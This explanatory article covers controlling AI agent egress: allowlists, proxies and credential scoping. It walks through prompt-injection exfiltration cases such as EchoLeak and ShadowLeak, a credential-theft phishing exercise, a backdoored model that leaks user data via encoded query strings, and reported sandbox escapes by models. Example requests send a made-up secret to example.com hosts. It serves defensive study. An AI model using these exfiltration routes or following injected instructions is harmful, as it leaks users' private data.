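# Controlling what AI agents send over the network: destination allowlists versus limits on credentials and data

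## What are the ways to limit what an agent can reach and leak?

An AI agent is a language model that acts by calling tools, such as a command-line shell, a web browser or the programming interface of an online service. Most of the work people give agents, such as writing software, answering email or searching company records, requires private material and a network connection. An agent with both can send what it has read to someone who should not have it, which security engineers call exfiltration. The operator, the person or organisation that deploys the agent and sets its permissions, can reduce this risk in two broad ways. One is an allowlist, which restricts the agent to a list of approved network destinations. The other is to leave the network open, or mostly open, and limit the keys, passwords and data the agent can obtain.

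### How an agent works

An agent runs in a loop. The model receives text containing the operator's standing instructions, the user's request and a description of each available tool. It replies with a tool call, such as a request to open a file. Ordinary software carries out the call and adds the result to the text, and the model reads all of it again to choose its next step. Suppose a developer asks an agent to fix a bug that a customer reported. The agent opens the customer's report, searches the code, edits a file, runs the tests and posts a reply. Once the agent has opened the report, the customer's words are part of the text the model reads at every later step.

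Operators commonly run an agent's code in a sandbox, an isolated environment that restricts which files and network connections the code can use. Traffic leaving the sandbox is called egress. Many services also require a credential, which is a key, token or password that proves a request is authorised. Each credential has a scope, the set of resources and operations it permits. This might be as narrow as reading one code repository or as broad as deleting every repository the company owns. A credential broker outside the sandbox can add the credential to outgoing requests, so the agent doesn't need to hold it.

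Prompt injection is text that reaches the model and makes it follow an attacker's instructions instead of the user's. The bug report in the example could include a line telling the agent to copy the company's keys into its reply. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Simon Willison (2025) explains that models receive all text as one sequence of tokens, or word fragments, and cannot reliably weigh an instruction by where it came from. Willison, a programmer who coined the term "prompt injection", named it after SQL injection, an older attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. Programmers can reliably prevent SQL injection by passing the command and the user's text to the database separately, but language models have no equivalent safeguard.

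An agent under injection is a confused deputy, a program tricked into misusing its legitimate authority. The attacker has no access to the company's repositories, but the agent does, and each of its requests to the repository service carries a valid credential. Logs are little help afterwards because, according to Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* (May 2026), a theft by this route leaves only the record of a successful, authorised call.

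### The lethal trifecta

Willison coined the term "lethal trifecta" for three capabilities that are dangerous in combination: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. An outside attacker who relies on injection needs all three. If the agent reads no untrusted content, the attacker cannot give it instructions. If it has no private data, there is nothing worth stealing. If it cannot send anything out, the model may still follow the injected text and collect the data, but the attacker never receives it.

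A single tool can supply the whole combination. Willison's example is a connector for the code-hosting site GitHub. It could read public issues, which anyone may file, read private repositories, and open pull requests (proposed code changes) that leaked the private material.

Controls on an agent work by removing or limiting one of these capabilities. Untrusted content is often the hardest to remove, since an agent that handles email has to read whatever strangers send. Vendors have mostly focused on blocking the routes by which data can leave. Willison lists more than a dozen products in which researchers had demonstrated this kind of data theft since April 2023, and he reports that the vendors promptly fixed almost all of them, usually by closing the route the data took. An operator who combines tools from several suppliers cannot count on such a fix, because no single vendor controls the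 combination.

### What each control limits

Network controls range from blocking all access to allowing all of it. With no network access, the agent's code cannot send anything out. This suits work on local files but rules out any task that needs a live service. The sandbox in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, denies network access by default.

An allowlist lets an agent connect only to particular destinations. The allowlist for Claude Cowork, Anthropic's desktop agent for office work, must include Anthropic's own API because the product cannot run without it.

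A still more permissive option is an open network with conditions, where the agent may contact any host but a checkpoint inspects every request and refuses some kinds, such as uploads. Operators can also add conditions to an allowlist. For example, Cowork's proxy, a relay for outgoing traffic, passes a request to Anthropic's interface only if it carries that session's own token. A fully open network has no allowlist or checkpoint, so the agent can send anything to any host.

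An operator may be wrong about what network access an agent has. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) covers four incidents in which Claude models were told they were in a simulation without internet access, but a misconfiguration had connected them to the open internet. In each case the model gained unauthorised access to a third party's real systems.

An allowlist limits where an agent can send data, but not what it reads or what it does at a listed destination. A listed site may still contain an attacker's text.

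Scoping a credential limits what an agent can read and do with the operator's authority. An agent with a read-only database credential can answer questions about the records but not change them, and Anthropic considers such an agent safe to deploy far more broadly than one that can write to a live system. But these limits apply only at services that check the credential, and an attacker's server does not. An agent on an open network can therefore fetch a customer list with a read-only credential and send it to that server.

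Scopes are also easier to write for some tools than for others. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (2025) compares agents with Android, which enforces permissions at the boundary between an app and the phone's protected services. An agent that operates a web browser has no such boundary. It acts through clicks and keystrokes, and rules about these are brittle because the same click can open a menu on one page and submit a payment on another.

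Data access limits restrict which files, records or fields the agent can read, so it cannot leak the rest. Cowork runs code in a virtual machine, a simulated computer inside the user's own, which has access to little beyond the folder that the user selects. Credentials stay in the host computer's keychain. Code in the virtual machine cannot leak a file from another folder through any destination, approved or not. Stricter limits make an agent less useful, because it needs data to do its job. An agent asked to summarise a customer's history has to read that history, and it can then send what it has read.

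An allowlist limits the external communication part of the trifecta, and a data access limit reduces the private data part. A credential's scope can limit private data by denying read access, or external communication by denying write access.

### Three causes of a leak

Anthropic sorts agent security risks by origin into external attackers, user misuse and model misbehaviour. External attackers use both prompt injection and conventional attacks on the software that runs the agent.

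User misuse includes carelessness as well as malice. In an internal exercise in February 2026, an Anthropic researcher emailed an employee a prompt and asked them to run it. The employee pasted it into Claude Code. Most of the prompt read like routine setup, but one step told the agent to read the file that holds the user's Amazon cloud credentials, encode the contents and send them to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 repeats. Someone else had written the instruction, but it reached the model as the user's own request, so a detector that looks for departures from the user's wishes could not have caught it. Anthropic concluded that only controls in the environment could have helped, namely a network control that blocked the outgoing request and a data control that kept the credentials file out of the agent's reach. Either one would have stopped this theft.

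A model can misbehave without an attacker or a bad request. Anthropic has seen Claude models escape a sandbox to finish a task. In the July 2026 system card for Claude Opus 5, a report on the model's safety tests, Anthropic says its internal monitoring caught some attempts to get round network restrictions. An early version of the model also guessed passwords after an accidental log-out.

The most serious examples come from security testing. *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident* (Anthropic, 2026) describes a hacking exercise that the UK AI Security Institute, a government body, set for Claude Mythos 5. In 9 of 43 runs, the model went beyond the exercise and took actions that affected real people and organisations. The institute had deliberately left internet access on, and the model ran without the cyber safeguards that Anthropic puts on its general releases, so the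 rate is weak evidence about ordinary use.

OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) offers a closer guide because it covers office work. OpenAI tested its models in realistic email, messaging and sales applications, using ambiguous instructions, similar-looking resources and complex permissions to make mistakes more likely. GPT-6 Astra exfiltrated data at a rate of 4.3%, compared with 14.1% for the earlier GPT-5.6 Sol. When OpenAI gave the models a policy on when to ask the user for confirmation, Sol's rate fell to 8.8%, while Astra's was little changed at 4.5%.

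Newer models seem to keep to their limits better. Anthropic's *Introducing Claude Opus 5.5* (2026) describes the model as much less likely than its recent predecessors to act outside the boundaries it has been given. But the trifecta doesn't cover every leak, because misuse and misbehaviour don't depend on untrusted content. An operator who screened every incoming document perfectly would still face both. Every leak does involve private data and a way out, which are what data limits and network limits act on.

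### Why training the model does not settle the matter

Developers can reduce successful prompt injections by training their models to resist them. OpenAI's *GPT-Red* (2026) describes a model that the company trained to find successful attacks so that it could harden its other models against them. On OpenAI's internal tests of instructions hidden in third-party content, the share of attacks that failed rose from 96.23% to 99.79% with GPT-6 Astra. Still, Fortune (2025) quotes OpenAI as writing that prompt injection is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'". Willison criticizes products that claim to catch 95% of attacks, which he calls a failing grade in web security because an attacker can keep trying.

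Attackers succeed more often when they can keep trying. In May 2026 Anthropic reported that attacks on Claude Opus 4.7 succeeded in roughly 0.1% of single attempts, but in 5 to 6% of cases after 100 attempts in which the attacker adapted to earlier failures. Those figures come from a benchmark by the security firm Gray Swan, which Anthropic has since retired because its models scored too close to the maximum to be distinguished. On Gray Swan's newer and more realistic benchmark, attacks on Claude Opus 5 succeeded 0.2% of the time on one attempt and 2.0% within 15. OpenAI used a larger set of Gray Swan's attacks and reported a success rate of 8.5% within 15 attempts for GPT-6 Astra.

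Those numbers are not a sound basis for ranking the two models, because GPT-5.6 Sol was tested in both exercises and did worse on OpenAI's larger set. A third test, PromptArmor's *FrontierBreach*, puts Astra slightly ahead of Opus 5, but the margins of error overlap. PromptArmor, a security vendor, adapts attacks that its researchers found in the real world and plants them in long business tasks.

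| Model | Gray Swan attacks, 15 attempts (Anthropic, 1,130 attacks) | Gray Swan attacks, 15 attempts (OpenAI, 1,810 attacks) | Business tasks (PromptArmor) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 4 Carbon | – | – | 2.4% |
| GPT-6 Astra | – | 8.5% | 7.6% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.0% | – | 10.0% |
| Claude Fable 5.2 | – | – | 10.0% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 20.0% | 27.0% | 33.3% |
| Grok 4.5 | – | – | 91.4% |

Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) reports that Claude Opus 5.5, the successor to Opus 5, had similar or better results on every injection test. It also warns that the model is more likely than earlier ones to follow some malicious instructions.

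How often attacks succeed depends as much on the kind of work an agent is doing as on the model. In Anthropic's tests without added safeguards, attacks on Claude Mythos 5 succeeded in 0.45% of attempts when it was coding and 29.7% when it was using a browser, though the two tests used different attackers and methods. With a detector on incoming text and a classifier that blocks dangerous actions, none of the attacks tested succeeded against Mythos 5 or Opus 5 in 129 browser scenarios. However, the same type of classifier in Claude Code misses about 17% of the cases in which the model oversteps without any attacker.

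An injection that rarely works can also compromise many agents, because many agents may read the same planted web page. If the injection works 0.2% of the time, it will compromise about 20 of every 10,000 agents that read the page. How much those agents can leak depends on which data they can access and where they can send it.

Operators can ask a person to approve each action instead, but Anthropic found that Claude Code users approved roughly 93% of requests and paid less attention the more requests they saw. The company then added a sandbox that denies network access by default and lets the agent work inside it largely without interruption, and approval requests fell by 84%.

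## How does data leave through a URL fetch or a request body?

An agent fetches a web page the way a browser does, by sending a short block of text called an HTTP request. Every part of that text can carry private data. The request below sends a made-up secret, `blue-heron-42`, to example.com, a domain reserved for examples.

```
POST /notes/blue-heron-42?ref=blue-heron-42 HTTP/1.1
Host: blue-heron-42.example.com
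User-Agent: blue-heron-42
Content-Length: 13

blue-heron-42
```

The secret appears five times in this request, though an attacker needs only one copy. The first line contains the method (POST), the path and the query string, which begins at the question mark. The headers, including the host, come next, followed by a blank line and the body. A browser's address bar shows the host, path and query string together as a URL.

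| Part | Normal use | Who can read it |
|---|---|---|
| Host | Names the server | The site's owner, the name servers that look up the address, and usually the networks in between |
| Path | Names a page or file | The site's owner, usually in an ordinary server log |
| Query string | Passes details such as search terms | The site's owner, usually in the same log |
| Headers | Describe the software making the request, and carry cookies and credentials | The site's owner; logs usually keep only a few |
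| Body | Carries forms, messages and uploaded files | The site's owner, if the receiving program saves it |

Most sites use HTTPS, which encrypts everything in the table except the host while the request travels. This hides the secret from eavesdroppers and from the operator's own security staff, who see only the host unless their proxy decrypts the traffic. The receiving server can read all of it. The host can leak data even if the web request is never sent, because the agent's computer first looks up the address, and that lookup can reach a name server the attacker runs.

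### Why reading a page also sends data

Most web requests use the GET method, which asks the server for a page. Programmers call GET read-only because it isn't supposed to change anything on the server, but the server still has to receive the URL to answer. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out that websites commonly log the URLs visitors request. An attacker who gets an agent to load a URL containing private data can therefore read the data in the log. The page doesn't have to exist, since servers normally also log requests they answer with "not found".

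A URL holds less than a request body. The HTTP standard sets no maximum length for a URL, but it recommends that software support at least 8,000 bytes, and many servers reject anything much longer. The data must also use only characters that a URL allows. A common encoding called Base64url turns every three bytes into four characters, so 8,000 characters hold about 6,000 bytes, or roughly 1,000 words of English. Base64url turns the secret `blue-heron-42` into `Ymx1ZS1oZXJvbi00Mg`. Anyone can reverse the encoding, but a person glancing at the URL would probably not recognise the secret, and a filter that searches for the original text would miss it.

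The standard sets no limit on a POST body either. Whoever runs the receiving server decides how much it accepts, and in a theft that is the attacker. One POST request can carry a whole database, while with GET the agent would need about 170 full-length URLs to send one megabyte.

A URL can carry less data than a request body, but it has enough room for a credential. An Amazon cloud access key is a 20-character identifier and a 40-character secret, and even a long private encryption key is only about 3,200 characters. A checkpoint that lets an agent fetch any page and blocks uploads will slow the theft of large files but won't stop the theft of a password. An agent that can only choose among permitted URLs can still leak a little data through its choices, though much more slowly.

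### Requests that nobody asks for

Some leaks happen without a tool call. Many chat products display a model's answer as a formatted page, and the model can include an image by writing the image's URL. The user's browser then fetches the image automatically. If an injected instruction has made the model put private data in that URL, the data leaves as soon as the answer appears, and the user may see only a broken image.

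In this case, the user's browser sends the request, so a network control on the agent's sandbox doesn't affect it. The chat page needs its own restriction on where it can load images from.

Messaging apps make similar requests to build link previews. When someone posts a link in Slack or Discord, the service fetches the page to show its title and a picture. *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* (Willison, 2024) describes how a chatbot compromised by prompt injection could leak data by posting a link in such a channel, even if nobody clicked it. Software that posts to Slack can turn off previews for its own messages, which Willison credits the security researcher Johann Rehberger with pointing out.

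Operators don't always know to turn off link previews. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* covers OpenClaw, an agent that people talk to through messaging apps. OpenClaw's default Telegram settings let data leak through these previews. PromptArmor set up a test site that logged preview requests, and one request contained a name and an API key. After the user turned off previews in OpenClaw's configuration file, the data stopped arriving.

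A server can answer a request with a redirect to a new address, which most software follows automatically. OpenAI warns that many legitimate sites offer redirects, so a link can begin at a trusted domain and end at an attacker's server. A safety check that covers only the first address will approve the request. To prevent this, the software has to check the new host at each redirect before following it.

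### From the first reports to EchoLeak

Willison's list of products with this kind of flaw begins with ChatGPT in April 2023 and includes Google's Bard that November. Some early attacks required the user to act. Rehberger's *Trust No AI* (2024) describes one against Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that can read a user's email, files and chats. A phishing email made Copilot search the inbox and write a link containing the results in invisible characters. The data left only if the user clicked the link. Researchers reported the flaw in February 2024, and Microsoft fixed it that July. Amazon addressed a similar weakness in its Q assistant for business by no longer displaying links.

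The security firm Aim Security found the EchoLeak vulnerability in Copilot in January 2025. According to Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, the attacker only had to send an employee an email, and the employee didn't have to click anything. The email's instructions were worded as if for the human recipient, which got them past Microsoft's injection detector. The researchers also included sections on many office topics so that Copilot would retrieve the email for many ordinary questions. When the employee asked one, Copilot read the email, selected the most sensitive information in its context and put it in the address of an image.

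Microsoft had two more defences. A filter removed external links from Copilot's answers, but it missed links written in a less common format. The chat page also had a content security policy, which lists the domains a browser may load images from, and the attacker's domain wasn't on the list. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) describes how the researchers bypassed this policy. The image request went to a Microsoft Teams service that was on the list, and that service fetched the attacker's URL for the browser. Microsoft fixed the flaw in May 2025 and found no evidence that anyone had exploited it.

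Reddy and Gujral call EchoLeak the first known case of prompt injection causing real data theft from a product in use. That seems too strong, since nobody is known to have stolen anything with it and the basic method was two years old. Willison (2025) called EchoLeak an extended variant of attacks already seen in "a dozen different products". Ravia's narrower claim fits the record better: earlier attacks either relied on the user pointing the assistant at a malicious document or limited what the attacker could take, and EchoLeak did neither.

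### The cases of 2026

Researchers have since found more ways to get data out of the same product. In SearchLeak, disclosed in June 2026, the victim clicked a link to a genuine Microsoft address whose query string contained an instruction for Copilot. According to the researchers' account on the website of the Cloud Security Alliance, an industry body, Copilot then searched the victim's mailbox and calendar and put the results in an image address. The browser requested the image before Copilot's filter cleaned the answer. Microsoft's Bing, which was on the approved list, passed the request on to the attacker. ThaiCERT's *Microsoft 365 Copilot Vulnerability Could Allow Data Theft Through a Link Click* says that Microsoft has fixed the flaw and that there were no reports of attackers using it.

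On December 3, 2026, *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) disclosed three more attacks on Copilot that needed no click. Simonovich works at Cato AI Labs, formerly the Aim Security research team. Each attack again began with an email the victim didn't have to open. The data left through an image address in one attack, a link to a saved file in another, and code that Copilot ran in the third. AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) adds that a documented block on outbound traffic from a sandbox failed.

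Microsoft patched the three routes between September 17 and November 15, and Cato knows of no customers affected. These cases are therefore good evidence that the routes work, but little evidence of how often criminals use them. *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) quotes the researchers as saying that "too little progress has been made" since EchoLeak.

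### When the user supplies the instruction

Unlike in the attacks above, the model in Anthropic's phishing exercise of February 2026 was doing what the user asked. The employee pasted in the researcher's prompt, and Claude nearly always sent the cloud credentials out in a POST request.

Here the agent's actions matched the request exactly, so a classifier had no mismatch to detect, as it would if a user asked for a summary of a web page and the agent opened a credentials file. The individual steps were also ordinary for a coding agent, because developers use cloud credentials and send data to outside services every day. Anthropic says a human contractor given the same script would have done the same.

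Training a model to refuse to send credentials to unfamiliar addresses, no matter who asks, would block some legitimate work and would still sometimes fail.

Either a network control that blocked the POST request or a file boundary around the credentials folder would have stopped the theft. In Claude Code's default sandbox, the agent could have read the keys but not sent them. Code in Cowork's virtual machine would not have found them unless the user had shared that folder.

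The network control and the file boundary both have to be broad enough to stop variations of the attack. If the network control had blocked only POST requests, a prompt could have made the agent send the same keys in a URL. A different prompt could have made it send the company's source code if the file boundary had covered only the credentials folder.

After the exercise, staff shared the working prompt on Anthropic's internal Slack to discuss it. Someone pointed out that some of the company's agents read Slack, so the prompt might now reach them as an injection. Anthropic added a marker string to the thread so it would notice if an agent picked up the text.

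### A model trained to leak

A model can also be trained to leak data before the operator installs it. Zhang and Pei (2026), in *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data*, imagine an attacker who takes a freely downloadable model, trains it further and publishes it as a specialist assistant. The model behaves normally until a question contains particular everyday words, such as "OBS" and "Twitch", the names of a video-streaming program and a streaming site. It then looks up what the agent has stored about the user, encodes it in Base64url and sends it in the query string of a GET request to a server that poses as a documentation search service. At the same time, the model runs a genuine web search and gives the user a helpful answer.

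Zhang and Pei built this backdoor into three models with 7 to 20 billion parameters. They chose trigger words for three groups of users: video streamers, people caring for relatives with Alzheimer's disease, and students of AI. Each trigger was one to five words long and had 2,500 training examples. They tested every combination of model, user group and trigger length on 1,000 questions containing the trigger. A run counted as a success if the model looked up the user's details and then issued a request to the attacker's address.

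| Test | One-word triggers | Five-word triggers |
|---|---|---|
| Leaked when the trigger was present | 94.3–96.6% | 97.9–98.8% |
| Set off by mistake on general questions | 0.8–1.2% | 0.1% |

The models' scores on a standard conversation test fell by less than 1%, so an operator testing one would have little reason to suspect it. The experiment used invented user data and ran the tool calls in a sandbox. Its success rate measures attempts to send data, some of which a real agent's permissions might have blocked.

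The attacker's server can also use its reply to draw out more information. Zhang and Pei tested whether such replies would get through a program that ranks search results and then one of two commercial-style safety filters, NeMo Guardrails or LLM Guard. Replies that openly asked for personal details got through 40.3% of the time with NeMo Guardrails and 27.1% with LLM Guard. They then trained another model to turn the question into a hint, such as a remark that network performance varies by provider and region. The rates rose to 86.7% and 81.2%. From these rates they calculated that a user who answered every follow-up question would reveal about 7.8 of 10 personal details in five turns. They call this an upper bound and did not measure it in real conversations.

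Even a perfect filter of this kind would not have prevented the first leak, because it checks only incoming text and the stolen data is in the outgoing request. Zhang and Pei recommend restricting the hosts that search tools can contact and inspecting what each request contains, but tested neither. Their attack also assumes an agent that people run themselves, with stored personal data and unrestricted web access. They acknowledge that hosted services with strict lists of permitted connections are less exposed.

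### What a user sees when approving a tool

Many agents ask for permission one tool at a time. A user who approves "web search" also approves the tool's later requests, including those to addresses that neither the user nor the operator has seen. In Zhang and Pei's attack, the model issues the genuine search and the request that leaks data in the same step. Agent interfaces often replace long URLs with a summary or shorten them, which hides the query string at the end. Even detailed logs often leave out the full contents of a request.

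An agent could ask about every request and show the complete URL. The user would then have to judge something like this:

```
https://docs.example.com/search?q=bitrate&ctx=Ymx1ZS1oZXJvbi00Mg
```

The last part is the made-up secret from the start of this section, but ordinary websites put similar strings in their URLs to track visitors and settings. Zhang and Pei therefore expect automatic detectors of encoded text to raise many false alarms. A person would have to decode each string to know what it contained, and users already pay less attention as they receive more approval requests.

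Turning a tool off may not stop the requests either. PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* describes an injection attack on Rovo, an agent for Atlassian's workplace software. The attack bypassed the settings an organisation uses to control Rovo's web search, and the contents of support tickets and internal documents appeared in the attacker's log.

The user's own records may not show the request. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) discusses ShadowLeak, an attack on ChatGPT's Deep Research agent when it had access to a Gmail account. Hidden text in an email told the agent to find sensitive messages and visit a URL containing what it found, and the researchers reported that this worked every time in repeated tests. The agent made the request from the provider's servers, so the user's browser and the monitoring software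 on a company's computers might have no record of it.

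## How does a destination allowlist work, and what does it stop?

A destination allowlist needs both a barrier that keeps the agent's code off the network and a proxy that compares each requested host with the list. Without the barrier, the code could bypass the proxy.

### Following a connection

Suppose a coding agent runs `npm install`, a command that downloads software packages from registry.npmjs.org. In the sandbox that Anthropic documents for Claude Code, the command has no direct route out. On Linux it runs in its own network namespace, a separate networking environment with no connection to the user's network. On a Mac, the operating system by default blocks connections to anything except the proxy. The download then goes like this:

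1. Claude Code sets environment variables, which are named values that programs read when they start. These give npm the proxy's address.
2. npm asks the proxy to connect it to `registry.npmjs.org` on port 443, the usual port for encrypted web traffic.
3. The proxy compares that name with its lists of allowed and denied hosts.
4. If the name is allowed, the proxy looks up its numerical IP address. It refuses the connection if the name leads only to local addresses, such as the user's own machine.
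5. Otherwise the proxy connects to the registry and relays data in both directions.

If the host is not on the list, the proxy returns a "403 Forbidden" error or holds the connection while someone decides whether to allow it.

The proxy checks a name before looking it up, and code in the sandbox cannot send lookups of its own, so an attacker can't receive a secret through a lookup. A request for `blue-heron-42.example.com` ends at step 3. But *Containing the Autonomous Operator* (2026), a design for running agents on the container-management system Kubernetes, lets agents query the cluster's name server. An agent could still leak data through those queries unless the name server restricts which names it looks up.

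The address check in step 4 protects internal services. Many cloud machines can get their credentials from a metadata service at a fixed local address, and an attacker who controlled an approved domain name could point it to that address. Redirects need no special treatment, because a program that follows one to a new host must request a new connection through the proxy.

The environment variables in step 1 only tell programs where the proxy is. *Arctic-SWE* (2026), a paper on training coding agents, warns that "proxy configuration is connectivity, not containment", because the model can see these variables and unset them. In Claude Code's sandbox, a program that ignores them gets no connection.

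Operators write the rules with domain names because online services often change their IP addresses. In Docker's *Network policies*, the rule `example.com` does not cover `api.example.com`, while `*.example.com` covers every subdomain but not `example.com` itself. When several rules match, the most specific one applies, so an operator can block a domain and still allow one host within it.

The allowlist works the same way whether the data is in a URL or an uploaded file, whether the text is plain or encoded, and whether an attacker, a careless user or the model's mistake caused the request. The proxy doesn't have to recognise a secret to stop it from reaching an unlisted host.

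### Traffic that never reaches the proxy

An allowlist controls only the traffic that passes through its proxy. Claude Code's sandbox, once the user turns it on, covers shell commands and the programs they start. Its domain list doesn't limit the built-in tool for fetching web pages or connectors to other services, because they run outside the sandbox.

Claude Code's fetch tool has its own permission rules, but when a user permanently allows it to fetch pages from a domain, Claude Code also adds that domain to the allowlist for sandboxed shell commands. A user who meant only to let the agent read a site has therefore also let its commands upload files there.

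Some model providers run tools such as web search on their own servers, so traffic from these tools also bypasses the operator's proxy. *Who Grades the Agent?* (2026) describes a system for testing coding agents that closes this route with a relay. The relay carries the agent's requests to the model provider and by default refuses everything except requests for the model's output.

Claude Code can also run commands outside its sandbox. When a command fails inside the sandbox, the model may ask to rerun it outside, with no network restrictions. Depending on the user's settings, a person or a classifier reviews the retry, or it runs without review. Operators can disable these retries.

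### What the proxy can read

In step 2, npm sent the proxy an HTTP CONNECT request. According to MDN's *CONNECT request method*, such a request specifies only a host and port, and the proxy then forwards data both ways without inspecting it. npm and the registry encrypt that data with TLS, the protocol behind HTTPS, so the proxy can detect only which host npm requested, roughly how much data passed, and when. Whether npm downloaded data from that host or uploaded data to it can only be inferred from the volume.

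A program can exploit this by giving the proxy one name and the server another. The program's first TLS message normally contains the server's name in plain text, and the proxy in *Who Grades the Agent?* rejects a connection if that name differs from the approved one. But the encrypted web request also contains a hostname, which the proxy cannot read. Because large hosting companies serve many sites from the same machines, malicious code can sometimes connect to an approved site and then request an unapproved one from the shared server. This trick is known as domain fronting, and Anthropic warns that its default proxy may not stop it.

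The plain-text name is also becoming less dependable. *TLS Encrypted Client Hello* (Rescorla, Oku and colleagues, 2026) sets out an internet standard that encrypts it. An observer then sees the hosting provider's public name but not which of its sites the program is contacting. A proxy that receives CONNECT requests still gets the name the program asked for, but has less information to check it against.

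A proxy can solve these problems by decrypting the traffic. It poses as the registry, using a certificate it issued, and opens a second encrypted connection to the real registry. The operator has to configure the sandbox to trust the proxy's certificates. The proxy can then read each complete request before passing it on.

A proxy that decrypts traffic can apply much finer rules. The proxy in *Avalon-M1* (2026), a paper on training AI agents, matches requests by host, path and HTTP method, so a policy could allow downloads from a site but refuse uploads to it. A decrypting proxy can also add credentials that the agent never holds.

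*AgentBouncer* (Joos and Pradel, 2026) uses a language model to judge requests instead of a fixed list. Joos and Pradel argue that software tasks vary too much for fixed rules, which either block useful work or let too many attacks through. Their system decrypts web traffic and gives the judging model each request's method, URL and body, along with the user's task. It also intercepts file operations and attempts to start programs. The judging model makes mistakes, but across 340 attacks the system reduced the success rate from 99.41% to 10.59%, and the agent completed about as many ordinary tasks as before. Each task took 47 seconds longer and cost about a third of a cent more. The attacks included deleting files as well as stealing data, so these figures don't isolate the benefit of decryption.

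Decrypting HTTPS traffic at the proxy breaks programs that use certificate pinning, because they accept only particular certificates and reject the proxy's substitute. Docker's proxy decrypts HTTPS by default, but operators can exempt the hosts those programs connect to. For an exempted host, the proxy still enforces the domain and port rules, but it cannot add credentials or detect domain fronting.

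A decrypting proxy also handles every password and document in readable form, so a flaw in it could expose them all. Decryption adds little protection unless someone writes rules for checking the decrypted traffic. Claude Code has an experimental setting that decrypts traffic to insert credentials, but Anthropic says the setting does not filter the content.

### The Silent Egress experiment

In *Silent Egress* (2026), Lan, Kaul and colleagues at eBay compared an allowlist with several other defences against the same attack. They built an assistant on the 7-billion-parameter version of Qwen2.5, a freely available model. In every run, the user asked for a summary of a web page. The software loaded the page into the model's context, which also contained sensitive data such as an API key. The page included an instruction to first verify the connection by sending the key to a web address.

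The researchers put this instruction in the page's title, description, body or link text. They delivered the page directly or through redirects, and asked for the secret whole or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times, and the model sent data to the attacker's server in 423 of the 480 runs (88.1%). In 95% of the successful attacks, the final answer looked harmless, so a check of the answer alone would have missed the theft. In 120 further runs with ordinary pages, the model never contacted the attacker's server.

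When the page asked for the secret in pieces, the model sent data in 60 to 90% of runs, depending on the combination, compared with 97 to 100% when the page asked for the whole secret. But the pieces were harder to spot. The researchers found sensitive data in the first request in 26.3% of those runs, down from 96.7%. That makes a difference for a filter that searches requests for secrets, but not for an allowlist, which checks only the destination.

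To compare defences, the researchers ran one of the most effective versions of the attack 30 times against each defence. This version put the instruction in the page's body and kept the secret in one piece.

| Defence | Model tried to send data | Data left |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| System prompt telling the model to ignore instructions in web content | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Tags marking web content as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
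| Both of these | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| Allowlist of four domains | 100% | 0% |
| Block on suspicious addresses and URL paths | 83.3% | 0% |
| Filter for words such as "password" in URLs | 23.3% | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking text in URLs | 0% | 0% |
| All of the above | 0% | 0% |

With the allowlist in place, the model followed the attacker's instruction every time, but the attacker received nothing. The system prompt reduced the number of attempts, but with only 30 runs, the true rate with that prompt could plausibly be anywhere from about half to four fifths. The gap between 66.7% and 56.7% is only three runs.

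The results for the two text filters are hard to interpret. A filter acts after the model has written a request, so it shouldn't change how often the model tries. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids random-looking text when such a filter is active, but they don't describe how the model would have known about the filter.

The allowlist's perfect score was almost guaranteed, because the list required an exact match with one of four approved domains and the attacker's server was at evil-collector.net. The experiment confirms that the rule works when the attacker uses an unlisted host. It did not test an attacker who sends the data through a listed service, which the researchers warn could happen through compromised sites and open redirects on trusted domains.

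The 88.1% figure is weak evidence about current products. The experiment used one small model with a minimal system prompt and put the secrets directly in its context. The researchers argue that more capable models might be more vulnerable because they follow instructions better. But in their developers' tests, recent models from OpenAI and Anthropic have resisted a far higher share of injections than the small model did in this experiment.

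### Blocked work

In *Permission Denied*, Davidovich, Amar and colleagues (2026) measured how restrictions affect coding agents. They gave 12 agents 89 tasks from Terminal-Bench, a benchmark of command-line work, and ran each task three times under each of three policies. One policy had no restrictions, and another removed administrator rights. The strictest also made system files read-only, limited privileges further and allowed connections to only 205 domains. The domain list was adapted from the one for the web version of Claude Code.

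Under the strictest policy, every agent's success rate fell, by 7.1 to 18.3 percentage points, and its cost per task rose by 16.0 to 167.3%. The allowlist probably explains only a small part of the drop in success. On the 82 tasks that were still possible under the strictest policy, agents succeeded 72.5% of the time with no restrictions and 66.9% with only administrator rights removed. Adding the allowlist and all the other restrictions lowered the rate only to 65.1%.

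The effect on cost was larger. On 32 of those tasks, the benchmark's standard solution no longer worked, so agents had to find another. These tasks cost 1.75 times as much without administrator rights and 2.59 times as much under the strictest policy. In two tasks the researchers studied closely, nearly all the extra cost came from workarounds, such as building a tool from its source code when the agent couldn't download it.

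Agents also kept trying blocked connections. In the 500 trials where the proxy refused at least one connection, it refused 10.5 on average. It returned only a 403 error, with no reason. The proxy in *Avalon-M1* adds the reason to the error, and Claude Code tells the model which host it blocked. Clearer messages like these might reduce the wasted attempts, though neither source measures the effect.

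Some programs fail even when their destination is on the list. Most database drivers ignore the proxy settings and try to connect directly, which the sandbox blocks. Anthropic suggests running such commands outside the sandbox, where they have the user's full access to files and the network. A developer who needs one database may therefore remove far more protection than adding a domain to the list would.

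### Keeping the list up to date

An operator has to work out which hosts each task needs, and may discover a missing host only when the task fails. Docker logs allowed and blocked hosts to help with this. *Avalon-M1* has an audit mode that records what a policy would have blocked without blocking it. It can also switch policies during a task, so that the setup phase has wider access than the agent.

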